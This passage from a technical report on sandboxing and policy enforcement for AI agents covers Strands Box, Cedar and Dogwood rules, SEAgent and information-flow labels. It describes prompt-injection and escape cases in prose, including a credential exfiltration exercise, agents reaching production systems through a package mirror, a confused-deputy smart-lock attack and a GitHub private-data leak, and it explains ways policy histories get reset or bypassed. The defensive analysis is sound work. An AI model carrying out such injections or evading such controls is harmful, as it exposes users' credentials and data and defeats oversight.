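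Running inside the virtual machine may make the proxy easier to tamper with, since it presumably depends on the agent not gaining full control there. Anthropic reports that only two of Cowork's six main isolation mechanisms operate outside the virtual machine's kernel and would still work if an agent gained that control.

An internal service can cause the same problem as a public one. Lee and Lee describe a July 2026 evaluation in which OpenAI agents had no direct internet access but were allowed to use a software-package mirror. The agents communicated with one another through the mirror on their way to reaching the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

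Keys are particularly useful to an attacker. In an internal Anthropic exercise in February 2026, a researcher persuaded an employee to start Claude Code with a prompt that looked like routine work. The prompt included a step to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside address, and Claude completed it in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic's defences in the model are designed to catch actions that depart from the user's wishes, but here the instruction had come from the user. Anthropic concluded that the only reliable protection was to block the connection and keep the credentials out of the agent's reach.

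### How Strands Box works

Strands Box, which AWS released in 2026 as an open-source developer preview, combines several of these defences on one machine. It runs on Macs with Apple's own chips, and AWS plans a Linux version. Help Net Security's *Strands Box* explains that it uses Seatbelt, the sandbox built into macOS, to confine the agent. The sandbox sends the agent's activity through four checkpoints:

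- a shell interpreter for commands;
- a Python interpreter for scripts;
- a broker for calls to MCP servers;
- a gateway for network traffic.

Every checkpoint submits the proposed action to the same local policy engine, which denies it unless a rule permits it. The engine uses a policy language called Dogwood. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) explains that Dogwood rules can take the agent's earlier actions into account. Brooker says the sandbox's job is to guarantee that "the policy layer is the only way out of the box."

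The checkpoints also write to one shared event history. Suppose a rule forbids web requests after the agent has read anything in a folder of customer data. The agent reads a customer file with a shell command, then runs a Python script that contacts a website. If each interpreter kept its own history, the Python interpreter would have no record of the earlier read and could allow the request. With a shared history, the engine finds the read and blocks the request.

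Strands Box keeps many keys away from the agent by giving it a placeholder. The process has three steps:

1. The agent's environment contains a meaningless token where a program would expect the real key.
2. The agent, or a script it has written, puts the token in a request as if it were the key.
3. If the policy allows the request, the network gateway replaces the token with the real key and sends the request on.

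An agent that prints all its environment settings therefore reveals only placeholders for these keys. Requests to AWS, however, carry a signature calculated from a secret key rather than the key itself, so the gateway signs each request for the agent.

Other products also separate credentials from the code that an agent runs. OpenAI's Agents SDK keeps credentials in the harness, outside the environment where model-written code runs, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI updates Agents SDK, adds sandbox for safer code execution* (2026). In Cowork, the user's credentials stay in the host's password store, and the virtual machine receives a session token with narrower permissions. An administrator can cancel that token without affecting the user's credentials.

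A placeholder prevents the agent from giving the key away, but not from misusing it, because the gateway adds the real key to any request that the policy allows, including one an attacker has suggested. Strands Box substitutes only the keys that somebody has configured, so a password in a readable file is unprotected. Hiding the user's keys would not have prevented the upload from Cowork either, because the attacker supplied a different key. To stop that kind of theft, a gateway must also reject keys it did not issue.

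### Strands Box as a reference monitor

Anderson required a reference monitor to be always invoked, tamper-proof and small enough to verify. Strands Box comes closest to meeting the first requirement, but it has a documented exception. An administrator can use the configuration file box.toml to give the agent direct access to chosen files. The operating system still confines the agent to those files, but its reads and writes there bypass the policy engine and are not recorded in the event history.

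This exception can disable a rule about other actions, such as web requests. If an administrator grants the customer-data folder directly, the agent can read a customer file without leaving any event in the history. The rule against later web requests is then not triggered, and the engine may allow the upload even though it is working correctly. To make a rule cover a file, the administrator has to leave the file off the direct list, so that the agent can reach it only through the interpreters.

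Whether Strands Box is tamper-proof depends partly on its setup. The kernel confines the agent, but an agent that could edit box.toml could give itself access to more files at the next start, and one that could delete events could reset a spending limit. Codex addresses a similar danger by giving the agent read-only access to Codex's settings folder and to the folder where the version-control program Git keeps scripts that run automatically.

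Agents may also help write the rules. Brooker admits that Dogwood policies can be hard to read and write, but says that the best coding agents already write them well. AWS supplies instructions to help them. Lee and Lee argue that an agent must never put into force a policy that it is subject to. The agent may draft a rule, but a separate service should accept it only with a person's approval. This stops the agent from changing the policy directly, but a hidden instruction could still shape the draft, and a reviewer who finds the language hard to read may well miss the change.

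Strands Box does not meet the third requirement in Anderson's sense. Its trusted computing base, meaning all the parts that must work correctly for a policy to hold, includes the macOS kernel, both interpreters, the MCP broker, the network gateway, the policy engine and the configuration. In remarks reported by Help Net Security, Brooker accepts that his team has added more code to trust, some of it complex, and that "bugs could mean bypassed policy." The team wrote it in Rust, a language that prevents many common memory errors, and tested it with fuzzing, which feeds a program large numbers of unusual inputs to expose faults. These methods reduce bugs but do not show that the code is correct. *Agenra* offers stronger assurance with its machine-checked proofs, but they cover a core of checking functions rather than a full Python interpreter.

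Anthropic's experience supports Brooker's caution. The established isolation software in its products has been dependable, but Anthropic's own proxy failed in the upload attack. Strands Box's interpreters and gateway are also new software that handles input an attacker may have influenced. A plain sandbox would have less code to trust, but it could not enforce a rule such as "push code only after the tests pass", because it does not track test results. For an agent with little access, the plain sandbox may be the better choice. The extra code is easier to justify when the company needs to allow an action only under some conditions.

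The trusted computing base usually extends well beyond the policy engine. In Lee and Lee's system, it includes the software that connects the organisations, the component that carries out data-handling duties, the publishing system, the approval service, the register of data classifications and the tool gateway. They also trust the human approver to be honest, but expect them to make mistakes under heavy load. They assume the model in every agent is hostile.

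### Rules that silently do not apply

A control can also fail because software never applies it. The documentation for landstrip, a small open-source sandbox, describes a rule that works differently on each operating system. An administrator can forbid writes to files whose names match a pattern, such as those ending in ".pem", a common extension for security keys. On Linux, the tool checks the pattern at each attempted write, so it protects new files as well as existing ones. On macOS, it protects only the files that match when the sandbox starts, and it logs a warning. On Windows, it doesn't enforce patterns. A company that tested the rule only on Linux could easily assume that its Windows machines had the same protection.

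A permission check can also leave a gap if it runs too late. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws that let code run in Claude Code before the user had agreed. Claude Code read a project's settings during startup, before asking whether the user trusted the folder, and an attacker who controlled the project could exploit this order. Anthropic now delays reading and running those settings until the user has agreed.

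A confidentiality label likewise protects a document only where software checks it. A company's search tool might check the label while a feature that summarises the same document does not. Changing a label can also change what a rule allows, even when the rule itself stays the same. Lee and Lee made 90 small edits to a data-sharing agreement and the classifications it relied on, and tested each against 344,512 requests. Six of the edits changed only a field's classification. All six altered which requests the system allowed, but an automated check that compared versions of the policy text passed every one. Lee and Lee propose sending classification changes to the same human review as policy changes, though they have not yet built the register this needs.

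One security control can interfere with another. Companies often install software that monitors employees' computers for signs of attack, but it cannot monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine because the isolation that confines the agent also keeps this software out. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, but acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

Software is safer if it refuses to start when it cannot apply a rule. If it starts anyway, an administrator can check for silent failure by attempting a forbidden but harmless action, such as writing to a dummy key file, on every operating system in use and through every available tool. If the action is blocked on one route, that is weak evidence that it will be blocked on the others. The tests also need repeating after updates, which can change what is confined, as when a change in Cowork's arrangement altered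 which components the virtual machine confined.

### Questions for a particular deployment

The following questions establish whether an agent can act without passing a given check:

1. **What still works when the gateway is off?** In a test environment, every action that the gateway is supposed to control should fail. Anything that succeeds has used another route.
2. **Which processes run outside the sandbox?** The list should include the agent loop, local MCP servers, startup scripts and any process that can exempt a command from the restrictions.
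3. **What can someone do at each permitted destination?** The answer should cover uploads, messages to other users and requests made with a stranger's key.
4. **Where are the real credentials?** If the agent can read a key, a rule at the gateway may not control how the agent uses it.
5. **Who can change the rules, labels, direct file grants and event history?** The agent should not be able to change any of them on its own authority, including by editing a file that the system will read at its next start.
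6. **Which files and calls never reach the policy engine?** A rule about earlier actions cannot take account of an action missing from the history.
7. **Will a program outside the sandbox later run something the agent wrote?** If so, the agent's output can take effect with that program's permissions.
8. **What happens when a check fails or cannot start?** If the harness carries on without it, anyone who can make the check crash can also bypass it.

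## Rules for single calls and for sequences of calls

Once every call has to pass a policy engine, the protection depends on the engine's rules. The gateway in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, the AWS platform for running agents, accepts rules written in Cedar or in Dogwood, the language that Strands Box uses. Cedar rules apply to each call by itself, while Dogwood rules can also depend on earlier calls.

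### How Cedar decides one call

AWS released Cedar as open source in May 2023. According to AWS's *Introducing Cedar, an open-source language for access control* (2023), the company proves safety and correctness properties of a formal model of the Cedar engine, then tests that the working code matches the model. The AgentCore feature that applies Cedar rules to tool calls became generally available in March 2026 (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*, 2026).

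A Cedar rule can refer to the principal (the user or agent making the request), the action (the tool), the resource (in AgentCore, the gateway) and the context, which includes the tool's arguments and the current time. The following pair, with names shortened, follows the pattern of examples in AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*:

```
permit (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
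when { context.input.amount <= 75 };

forbid (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
when { context.input.orderDate.offset(duration("30d"))
       < context.system.now };
```

The first rule permits refunds of up to $75. The second forbids refunds on orders more than 30 days old. For a call *q*, let *P*(*q*) be the set of permit rules that match it and *F*(*q*) the set of forbid rules that match it. The engine allows *q* exactly when

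*P*(*q*) ≠ ∅ and *F*(*q*) = ∅.

So the engine denies a call by default, and one matching forbid overrides any number of permits.

Suppose that on 1 October an agent requests a $60 refund for an order dated 20 September. The permit matches because 60 is at most 75. The forbid doesn't, because 30 days after the order is 20 October, which is still in the future. The engine allows the call. If the agent then requests $60 for an order dated 1 August, both rules match and the engine denies the call. (A $90 refund on a recent order also fails, because no permit matches it.)

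Cedar has no loops and keeps no record of earlier calls, so the order in which the engine evaluates the rules doesn't affect the result. AgentCore can also identify tools that the rules would always deny and leave them off the list the agent receives, much as Uppala's proxy did.

The engine compares values exactly, but the values may be wrong. AWS points out that a customer's tier comes from a signed token, which the model cannot alter, whereas the tool's arguments come from the model. This does little harm for the refund amount, because the tool pays the same amount that the engine checked. But if the model writes 20 September as the date of an August order, by mistake or because of an injected instruction, the engine allows a refund it should have refused. To prevent this, either the refund tool has to look up the date itself, or the rule has to compare the date argument with something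 the agent could not have made up.

### Permitted calls with a forbidden result

An engine that enforces a single-call policy allows a sequence of calls whenever the policy allows each call in it. If the policy allows *a* and *b*, the engine must also allow *a* followed by *b*. An administrator who wants to prevent only that combination has to forbid one of the two calls altogether.

AWS's *Control agent behaviors and cost beyond a single action* gives the example of an agent that places a series of orders, each below the amount that needs approval. With a threshold of $1,000, ten orders of $900 would spend $9,000 without approval. In another example, an agent looks up a customer's account and then transfers money to a different account number. Reading a customer file and posting to Slack, the workplace chat service, can each be routine, but a company may not want the agent to do one right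 after the other.

A developer could have the application keep a running total and pass it to Cedar in the context. Dogwood does this bookkeeping in the policy engine.

### How Dogwood uses earlier calls

AWS released Dogwood around the end of July 2026. Any Cedar rule is also a valid Dogwood rule. Dogwood adds a second type of condition, marked "when temporal", which refers to a log of earlier events. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* lists three kinds of event: a request, a response (recorded with the tool's output when the tool succeeds) and an error. When a call arrives, the interpreter checks the temporal condition against the log and puts the result in a context field, as InfoQ explains. Cedar then decides as usual.

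A rule limiting the agent to three Slack posts in ten minutes, built on AWS's pattern for rate limits, would look like this:

```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"slack_post", resource)
when temporal {
  exists (n: Long).
    (count for (t: Timepoint). where
      (formerly within 10m
        (Action::"slack_post"::request{eventResource: resource}
         && tp(t)))) == n
    && n > 3
};
```

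The expression counts the Slack requests from the past ten minutes, including the current one, and calls the total *n*. The rule needs an ordinary permit beside it, since a forbid alone never allows anything. Here is how the engine would decide five posts:

| Time of post | Count | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| 9:00 | 1 | Allow |
| 9:02 | 2 | Allow |
| 9:05 | 3 | Allow |
| 9:08 | 4 | Deny |
| 9:11 | 3 or 4 | Depends on whether the denied post counts |

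AWS's explanations appear to differ on the last row. According to its reference documentation, the log records a request event for each authorised request and an error event for a denied one, so the count at 9:11 would be 3. But according to AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, denied attempts count towards a similar limit on refunds. On that basis the count would be 4, and an agent that kept retrying would stay locked out. A company that depends on either behaviour should test it.

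The second rule, a version of the one in the Strands Box example, blocks outbound requests once the agent has read customer data:

```
forbid (principal,
        action in [Action::"web_request", Action::"send_email",
                   Action::"slack_post"],
        resource)
when temporal {
  formerly within 24h
    Action::"read_customer_file"::request{eventResource: resource}
};
```

Suppose other rules permit all four tools.

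1. At 10:00 the agent fetches a web page. The log contains no customer file, so the forbid doesn't match and the engine allows the call.
2. At 10:05 the agent reads a customer file. The engine allows this too, and the log gains an event.
3. At 10:06 the agent tries to send figures to a website. The engine searches the past 24 hours, finds the event from 10:05 and denies the call.

As with Strands Box, the rule works only if the log records every way of reading the file. It is also so broad that the agent can't check the weather after reading one customer file. Rules based on data labels can be more selective.

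The choice between request and response events matters in both examples. The gateway records a response shortly after the tool finishes, so a customer-data rule that waited for the response could briefly fail to apply after the agent had received the file. In a case that InfoQ relays from AWS, an agent with a $5,000 spending limit starts three $2,000 transfers at once. A rule that adds up responses allows all three because none has been recorded yet. If the rule adds up requests instead, the totals are $2,000, $4,000 and $6,000, and the engine denies the third transfer.

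Dogwood can also help with the false order date. AWS shows a rule that permits a transfer only if a lookup in the past hour returned the same account number. A refund rule could likewise require that an earlier lookup of the same order returned the same date. This catches invented values, but it is weaker against prompt injection. An attacker who can get the agent to transfer money to account X may also be able to get it to look up account X first. The rule would then permit the transfer, unless the lookup tool restricts which accounts the agent can find.

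### When the history is lost

The log covers one session, and whoever calls the gateway chooses the session's identifier. AWS's *Temporal policies* explains that a new identifier starts a new count. AWS therefore warns in its rate-limit documentation that these limits are no defence against a determined caller. If fixed code in the harness sets the identifier, the model may be unable to change it, but an agent that can write its own requests to the gateway might pick a new one.

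Losing the count of Slack posts is a nuisance, but losing the record of a customer-data read is worse, because the model's context may still contain the data when the conversation continues under a new identifier. The record can be lost even without an attacker, because a temporal condition can look back at most 24 hours, and adding or updating a temporal rule ends every active session on that engine. The next request then fails, and the replacement session starts with an empty log. A carefully designed harness would therefore clear the model's context whenever it opens a new session.

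Dogwood also can't add up transfers across a customer's sessions. AgentCore has separate limits on each user's requests and tokens, but they apply per second or per minute and don't count the money transferred. The payment system is a better place to enforce a daily limit on transfers because it has a record of all of them.

### What a monitor cannot enforce

Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) examines which policies a monitor can enforce by watching a program's steps and stopping the program before it breaks a policy. One of his example policies forbids sending anything after reading a file, which is very close to the customer-data rule. Its monitor needs only two states. It starts in one that permits everything, and a file read moves it to the other, where it blocks every send.

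Such a monitor can base its decisions only on the steps taken so far, so it can enforce a policy only if every violation becomes definite after some finite number of steps. If a complete run σ of the agent, which may never end, breaks the policy, there must be some *i* such that every possible continuation of its first *i* steps, σ[..*i*], breaks it too. Policies that meet this condition are called safety properties, and they state that something bad never happens. A limit of three Slack posts in ten minutes is a safety property, because once a fourth post has gone out in that time, nothing the agent does later can undo the violation.

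"Every complaint eventually gets a reply" is a liveness property, which states that something good will eventually happen. No finite record violates it, because the reply could still come at the next step. The monitor therefore never has grounds to stop the agent, and stopping it would only make a reply less likely.

If the policy sets a deadline, such as a reply within 24 hours, a monitor can detect when the agent misses it. But refusing further tool calls doesn't send the reply, so other software or a person has to do that. A company can also rewrite the duty as a prohibition, such as a rule against closing a complaint before replying, though an agent could comply by leaving the complaint open forever. InfoQ reports that liveness properties are on Dogwood's roadmap, but enforcing them would require more than the power to refuse calls.

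### Rules about paths between agents

The customer-data rule names particular tools, so an administrator has to revise it whenever the company adds another way to send data. In a system of several agents, one agent can also ask another to do something it is not allowed to do itself. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) addresses both problems with a system called SEAgent. The paper defines privilege escalation as any action beyond the minimum needed for the user's request. Since nobody can list that minimum in advance, SEAgent's rules approximate it using attributes of the agents, tools and databases involved.

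In SEAgent, each tool has five attributes: what it acts on (local, external or physical), whether it reads, writes or executes, its sensitivity, whether its results are trusted, and whether they are personal. Agents have a trust attribute, and the databases they retrieve text from have trust and privacy attributes. As the agents work, SEAgent builds a graph. A tool call adds an arrow from the agent to the tool, a result adds one back, and a message adds an arrow between agents. A rule specifies a path in this graph and conditions on the attributes along it.

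In Ji and colleagues' main example, a user installs a web-search agent from an outside source. Its hidden instructions tell it to ask the house's smart-lock agent to unlock the front door before each search. It has no access to the lock, but it broadcasts the request and the smart-lock agent obeys, a confused deputy made of two agents. SEAgent records the path

search agent → smart-lock agent → UnlockDoor.

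One of SEAgent's rules denies any path from an unverified agent to a tool of more than low sensitivity, however many agents lie between them. Other rules cover paths from untrusted tool results and untrusted databases, and the emailing of sensitive personal data. To defend against malicious users, SEAgent relies on keeping each user's history separate.

Ji and colleagues tested the rules on InjecAgent and AgentDojo, two collections of simulated prompt-injection attacks, and used API-Bank, a set of tool-use tasks, to measure how well the agent did ordinary work. For some of the API-Bank tests, they turned on SEAgent's memory component, which clears the agent's context after each round and uses a model to choose which earlier entries to restore.

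| Measure | Unprotected agent | SEAgent |
|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks, AgentDojo | 39.14% | 0% |
| Successful attacks through a poisoned database, by type of harm | 50–80% | 0% |
| Correct tool calls, two-tool tasks, memory off | 79.27% | 71.34% |
| Correct tool calls, two-tool tasks, memory on | 74.39% | 50.00% |
| Correct tool calls, all tasks, memory on | 72.97% | 68.29% |
| Average time, one-tool tasks, memory on | 1.83 s | 5.79 s |

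The zeros are good evidence that four short rules can cover many known attacks, provided that the attributes are right. A model assigned the attributes, and people corrected its mistakes. The utility results are more mixed than the paper's summary of "negligible usability degradation" suggests, because utility fell on two-tool tasks. With memory off, SEAgent wrongly blocked none of the tasks that needed one or two tools, but 5.13% of those that needed three or more.

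In both wrongly blocked tasks, the agent used Wikipedia before recording health data or booking an appointment. Ji and colleagues suggest labelling Wikipedia as trusted, which would solve this. But anyone can edit Wikipedia, so the change would also let an attacker's text there lead to the same actions.

There is less evidence on multi-agent systems. The smart-lock attack was a single case study. In a larger multi-agent benchmark, overall success rose from 71.97% to 74.24% on travel tasks and from 52.46% to 63.11% on mortgage tasks, while token use fell by about a third or more. But these tests ran without labels or policy enforcement, so the gains come from the memory component. Rule checks took less than 6 milliseconds on average.

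SEAgent also differs from Cedar in allowing any call that no rule matches, so it fails open if a rule is forgotten. When a rule requires asking the user, the user can choose to allow the same path permanently. This is convenient but makes the control discretionary at that point. The four tested rules don't offer this choice because they all deny outright.

*AgentGuard* (Luo, Peng et al., 2026) describes a lighter attribute-based design. Developers add about ten lines of code to an existing agent, which then sends the details of each tool call to a central server. The server can apply fixed rules, consult a model or ask a person. The added code enforces the server's decision but, like a hook in the harness, can miss what a script does after it starts. The paper reports no measurements of security or speed.

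### Who writes the rules

Most companies already have their rules in ordinary prose, and AWS offers a tool that uses a language model to translate them into Dogwood. According to AWS, the tool first splits the document into single rules and sets aside those that Dogwood cannot express. The model then translates the rest. A compiler checks that each result is valid code and refers only to tools and fields that exist, and returns any errors to the model for another attempt.

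Some rules fail at the second step. "Act in the customer's best financial interest" doesn't specify an action to check. A rule that Social Security numbers must be redacted would require the engine to change a call, but the engine can only permit or deny calls. Rules that depend on weekends or bank holidays also fail, because Dogwood can't identify those days.

Ambiguous rules are more dangerous than rules that can't be translated, because the model can still translate them. For example, "No more than three transfers per hour" could mean three by one caller or three to one account. Both versions compile, so the engine will enforce whichever one the model guessed.

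Formal analysis can find some mistakes in rules written in plain Cedar. It turns the rules into logical formulas and checks them for every possible request. It can find a rule that never permits anything, such as AWS's example of one that requires a customer's tier to be both gold and platinum. It can also find a rule that always permits an action, or a forbid rule that completely cancels a permit rule. When someone changes the rules, the analysis can determine whether the new version allows any calls that the old one did not. In one of AWS's examples, an added condition looks like a restriction but sits inside an exception, so the change allows more orders.

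Such analysis cannot show whether the author intended the change, or whether a refund limit of 750 should have been 75. Cedar's analysis tools don't support Dogwood's temporal conditions at all. According to InfoQ, this is why Dogwood was created as a separate language.

AWS's *Securing AI agents with temporal policies in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) gives seven sample rules for a private bank's trading agent, but in the copy on HKU SPACE's AI Hub, several don't match their descriptions. One rule is supposed to stop the agent from trading after 15 minutes without contact with the adviser, but it does the reverse and permits trades unless there has been contact in the past 15 minutes. A $60,000 cap on trading adds up the cost field of price lookups instead of trades. The check that a trade uses the right client's portfolio compares the profile number instead of the portfolio number.

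The larger mistake is in how the rules combine. All seven are permits, and in Dogwood one matching permit is enough to allow a call. The rule that requires approval for large trades permits any trade under $25,000 by itself, even if the price is stale. Combined with the reversed rule, this would let an agent make a trade of any size as its first action in a session.

A compiler might catch the cap and the portfolio check, if those tools lack the fields used in the rules. It would accept the reversed condition and the seven permits, because they are valid code. The fix is to write one permit for trading and a separate forbid for each requirement. For example, one forbid would block trades unless the adviser has been in contact within 15 minutes.

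Testing the whole set of rules together would have exposed the problem. AWS supplies expected decisions for each rule. One is a denial for a trade 20 minutes after the last contact with the adviser, but the rules as printed would allow that trade. AgentCore has a mode that logs decisions without enforcing them, so a company can run such test cases before relying on a rule. Whoever owns the written policy should choose the expected decisions, preferably before reading the generated code, and include calls just below and just above each limit.

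## Confidentiality and integrity labels on an agent's data

The Dogwood rule that blocks web requests after an agent reads a customer file depends on which tool the agent called. On GitHub, an agent can use the same tool to read public and private files, so a rule based only on the tool applies equally to both. Information-flow control attaches labels to the data instead. Software copies each label to anything made from the data and checks it before the agent acts.

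### Ordering labels in a lattice

Denning (1976) worked out the mathematics of information-flow labels in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. She observed that most access controls of the time checked each access separately and ignored the paths that several permissions opened together. Her model has a set of labels, a "may flow to" relation ⊑ like Bell and LaPadula's, and an operation, now usually called the join and written ⊔, that gives the label of anything computed from two inputs.

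The simplest version has two labels for confidentiality, with public ⊑ secret, and two for integrity, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. Trusted data may go anywhere that untrusted data may go, but untrusted data may not be used where trusted data is required. An agent's data needs both kinds of label, so each item carries an (integrity, confidentiality) pair. The least restrictive pair is (trusted, public) and the most restrictive is (untrusted, secret). Neither (trusted, secret) nor (untrusted, public) may flow into the other, and their join is (untrusted, secret).

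A join has to satisfy two conditions:

- A ⊑ A ⊔ B and B ⊑ A ⊔ B;
- if A ⊑ C and B ⊑ C, then A ⊔ B ⊑ C.

When a program combines two pieces of data, the label on the result, called the join, must be at least as restrictive as the label on each input. Otherwise, Denning argues, a program allowed to compute *a* + *b* could set *b* to zero and so copy *a*. The join must also be no more restrictive than necessary. If a program may copy *a* and *b* separately to a place labelled C, it can combine them there, so forbidding it to move the combination would achieve nothing. Labels form a lattice if every pair has such a join and there is a lowest and a highest label.

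Joining two public labels always gives a public label, so a lattice can't mark two facts as sensitive together if each is harmless separately. An administrator worried about a particular combination has to label one of the facts secret from the start or write a separate rule.

Denning also distinguishes objects with a fixed label from objects whose label changes with their contents. For an agent, a public web page has the fixed label public, so the policy engine only has to check whether the data may flow to it. The model's context has a changing label, which becomes more restrictive as the agent reads.

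### Sets of readers and writers

A company has many secrets meant for different people, so the single label "secret" is often too crude. Costa and colleagues also describe confidentiality labels that list everyone who may read the data, and integrity labels that list everyone who could have written it.

Suppose a program joins two texts, *x* and *y*. Someone needs permission to read both before reading the combination, so the program intersects the reader sets. But anyone who could have written to either text could have influenced the combination, so it unites the writer sets:

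readers(*xy*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

writers(*xy*) = writers(*x*) ∪ writers(*y*)

Both operations make the label more restrictive, by leaving fewer permitted readers or more people to distrust. Reader sets are therefore ordered by reverse inclusion, so S₁ ⊑ S₂ means S₂ ⊆ S₁. The reader set of public data contains everyone, and the most restrictive reader set is empty.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* applies this to a user called Alex, who asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. One is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't authorised to learn them yet. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes has the reader set

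{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

The agent therefore may not send its reply to Marco automatically. If Priya had copied Marco into her email, the result would have been

{Alex, Priya, Marco} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex, Marco},

and the reply could go.

In this example the label prevents an ordinary mistake, not an attack, but it also blocks harmless replies. The agent can't thank Marco without Alex's approval, because the label depends on what the agent has read and not on what the reply contains. It can't answer Priya automatically either, since Marco's email wasn't addressed to her. If the agent had answered Marco before opening Priya's email, the label would have been {Alex, Marco} and the reply would have gone through.

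### How the agent loop tracks labels

Costa and colleagues add labels to the agent loop by giving the context a label of its own. This context label is the join of the labels of everything currently in the model's context. In the basic version, one turn works like this:

1. The harness labels the developer's instructions and the user's message, normally as trusted and public.
2. It sends the context to the model and gives the model's response the context label, joined with the label of the tool descriptions.
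3. If the response is a tool call, the function name and every argument inherit the response's label.
4. The policy engine checks the labelled call, and the run stops if the call breaks a policy.
5. Otherwise the tool runs, and its result receives a label ℓ.
6. The harness adds the result to the context and changes the context label from *C* to *C* ⊔ ℓ.

The label in step 5 depends on the call as well as on the data. For a function *f* with arguments labelled ℓ₁, …, ℓₙ,

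ℓ = ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ ⊔ *D*,

where ℓ_f is the label on the choice of function and *D* is the join of the labels of all stored data that *f* may read. Under this rule, even a lookup in a trusted company database can give an untrusted result. This makes sense if a hidden instruction prompted the lookup, because the attacker has then influenced which record the agent receives.

Any stored data that the tool may write gets the same label. If an agent reads a stranger's email and then saves a note, the note is untrusted, and remains so when another session opens it a week later. Dogwood's log covers a single session, so it can't pass that information to later ones. Labels can persist across sessions only if the storage keeps them, and an ordinary text file has no obvious place for one.

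A tool can label its result as a whole or in parts, such as each email in a list. The basic loop loses this detail when it puts everything into one context. Costa and colleagues' full system, FIDES, can keep the more restricted parts in variables that the planner doesn't see. Step 2 cautiously assumes that every part of the context influenced the model's response, because the harness can't determine precisely which parts did.

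### A trusted context and permitted readers

Costa and colleagues give two basic policies for the check in step 4. The trusted-context policy allows a consequential action, such as sending an email or deleting a file, only if nothing untrusted could have influenced the call:

integrity(ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ) = trusted.

The permitted-readers policy applies to data that leaves. If *S* is the set of people who may read an outgoing argument and *R* is the set of people who can read the channel, the call may go ahead only if

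*R* ⊆ *S*.

Costa and colleagues write this as *S* ⊑ *R*, which is equivalent because their order reverses set inclusion. For an email, *R* contains the recipients. For a public web page, *R* is everyone, so only public data may go there. In Alex's case, *S* is {Alex} and *R* is {Marco}, so the check fails.

The table shows what happens under each policy if sending and deleting both count as consequential.

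| Proposed action | Trusted context only | Permitted readers only | Both policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Send Priya a summary of a trusted sales file that she may read | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| Send that summary to Marco by mistake | Allow | Block | Block |
| Send Priya a false warning, prompted by a public web page | Block | Allow | Block |
| Delete a folder, prompted by a public web page | Block | Allow | Block |
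| Post the sales file publicly, prompted by a public web page | Block | Block | Block |

The permitted-readers policy limits the damage prompt injection can do but doesn't prevent the injection itself. An attacker who controls the agent still can't send data directly to anyone outside that data's reader set. The policy doesn't cover deletion, because deleting data doesn't send it anywhere.

The trusted-context policy alone lets confidential data leave, but prevents an attacker from causing this through untrusted data. Costa and colleagues compare this to robust declassification, in which a program may relax a confidentiality label only when an attacker cannot influence the decision. They say such disclosures can be assumed to be intentional. This is generous to a language model, which can pick the wrong recipient without any attacker, and they acknowledge in their threat model that models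 make mistakes.

Applying both policies stops the leak to Marco and the actions prompted by the web page. But it makes the agent much less useful, because the agent can't send even a harmless message after reading untrusted text. The policies also don't catch every mistake, since an agent in a trusted context can still send Priya the wrong figure.

Costa and colleagues don't treat replies to the user as consequential, so the basic check covers only tool calls. But replies can leak data if the chat window automatically loads images or previews from links, because the web address can contain the data. Microsoft suggests treating links to any host that isn't on an approved list as public channels. A policy can also use the sequence of earlier actions along with the labels, so the same engine could both check labels and limit how many messages an agent sends.

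### Labels in MCP messages

An agent often uses tools on servers that other companies run, so its harness needs a way to exchange labels with those servers. In June 2026, Microsoft described prototypes that do this over MCP, whose messages have a metadata field called `_meta`. The server puts labels in this field when it returns a result, and the harness does the same when it makes a call. Software that doesn't support labels can still exchange the messages, but it won't enforce the labels.

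Parts of a message may need different labels, so the prototypes use JSONPath, a notation for identifying parts of structured data. The path `$` refers to the whole call, and `$.arguments.content` refers to the text the agent wants to send. In Microsoft's example of a message to Teams, its workplace chat service, the call as a whole is labeled untrusted and public, while the text is labeled trusted and readable only by two named users. An outsider could therefore have influenced the decision to send the message, but not its text.

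Servers can also publish a policy for each tool in the metadata. The prototypes use Rego, an existing policy language, and each policy returns allow, deny or ask. Microsoft's policy for Teams messages works as follows:

1. If the context is trusted, allow the message.
2. Otherwise, look up the channel's members and allow the message if all of them may read the text.
3. Otherwise, ask the user, and list the people who would gain access.

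The announcement in the example can go to a channel containing only the two permitted users. If the channel has a third member, the harness asks before sending it. Looking up the members at the time of the call includes anyone who joined recently. But an empty member list would pass the test, so the engine needs to treat a failed lookup as an error rather than an empty list.

This policy is weaker than the strict combination of both basic policies, which allows a message only when the context is trusted and all the channel's readers are permitted. The Teams policy allows a message automatically when either condition holds. A hidden instruction still can't leak the text without the user's approval, but it could make the agent send a misleading message to people who are allowed to read the text. Applied to Alex's inbox, the Teams policy would even let the sales figures go to Marco if the harness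 treated emails from colleagues as trusted.

The harness also has to trust whoever supplies the labels. A malicious server could label its own text as trusted and publish a policy that allows everything. Because users can install MCP servers from many sources, an administrator would need to decide which servers may label data as trusted. The harness could then treat data from all other servers as untrusted.

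### A public issue and a private repository

Microsoft's other example is a prompt-injection attack that researchers had demonstrated about a year earlier. The user sofiagarcia opens an issue (a bug report or request) in a public GitHub repository, requesting a comment that contains information from a private repository, contoso/core. An agent working for alexmurphy_contoso, who has access to the private repository, handles the issue. The agent is allowed to read the private repository and to comment on the public one, so checking each permission separately doesn't stop the attack.

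One defence is to narrow the access token, the credential that determines what the agent may do on GitHub. GitHub (2026) announced in January that its MCP server automatically filters tools according to the token's permissions. This defence doesn't help if the user needs a token that covers both repositories.

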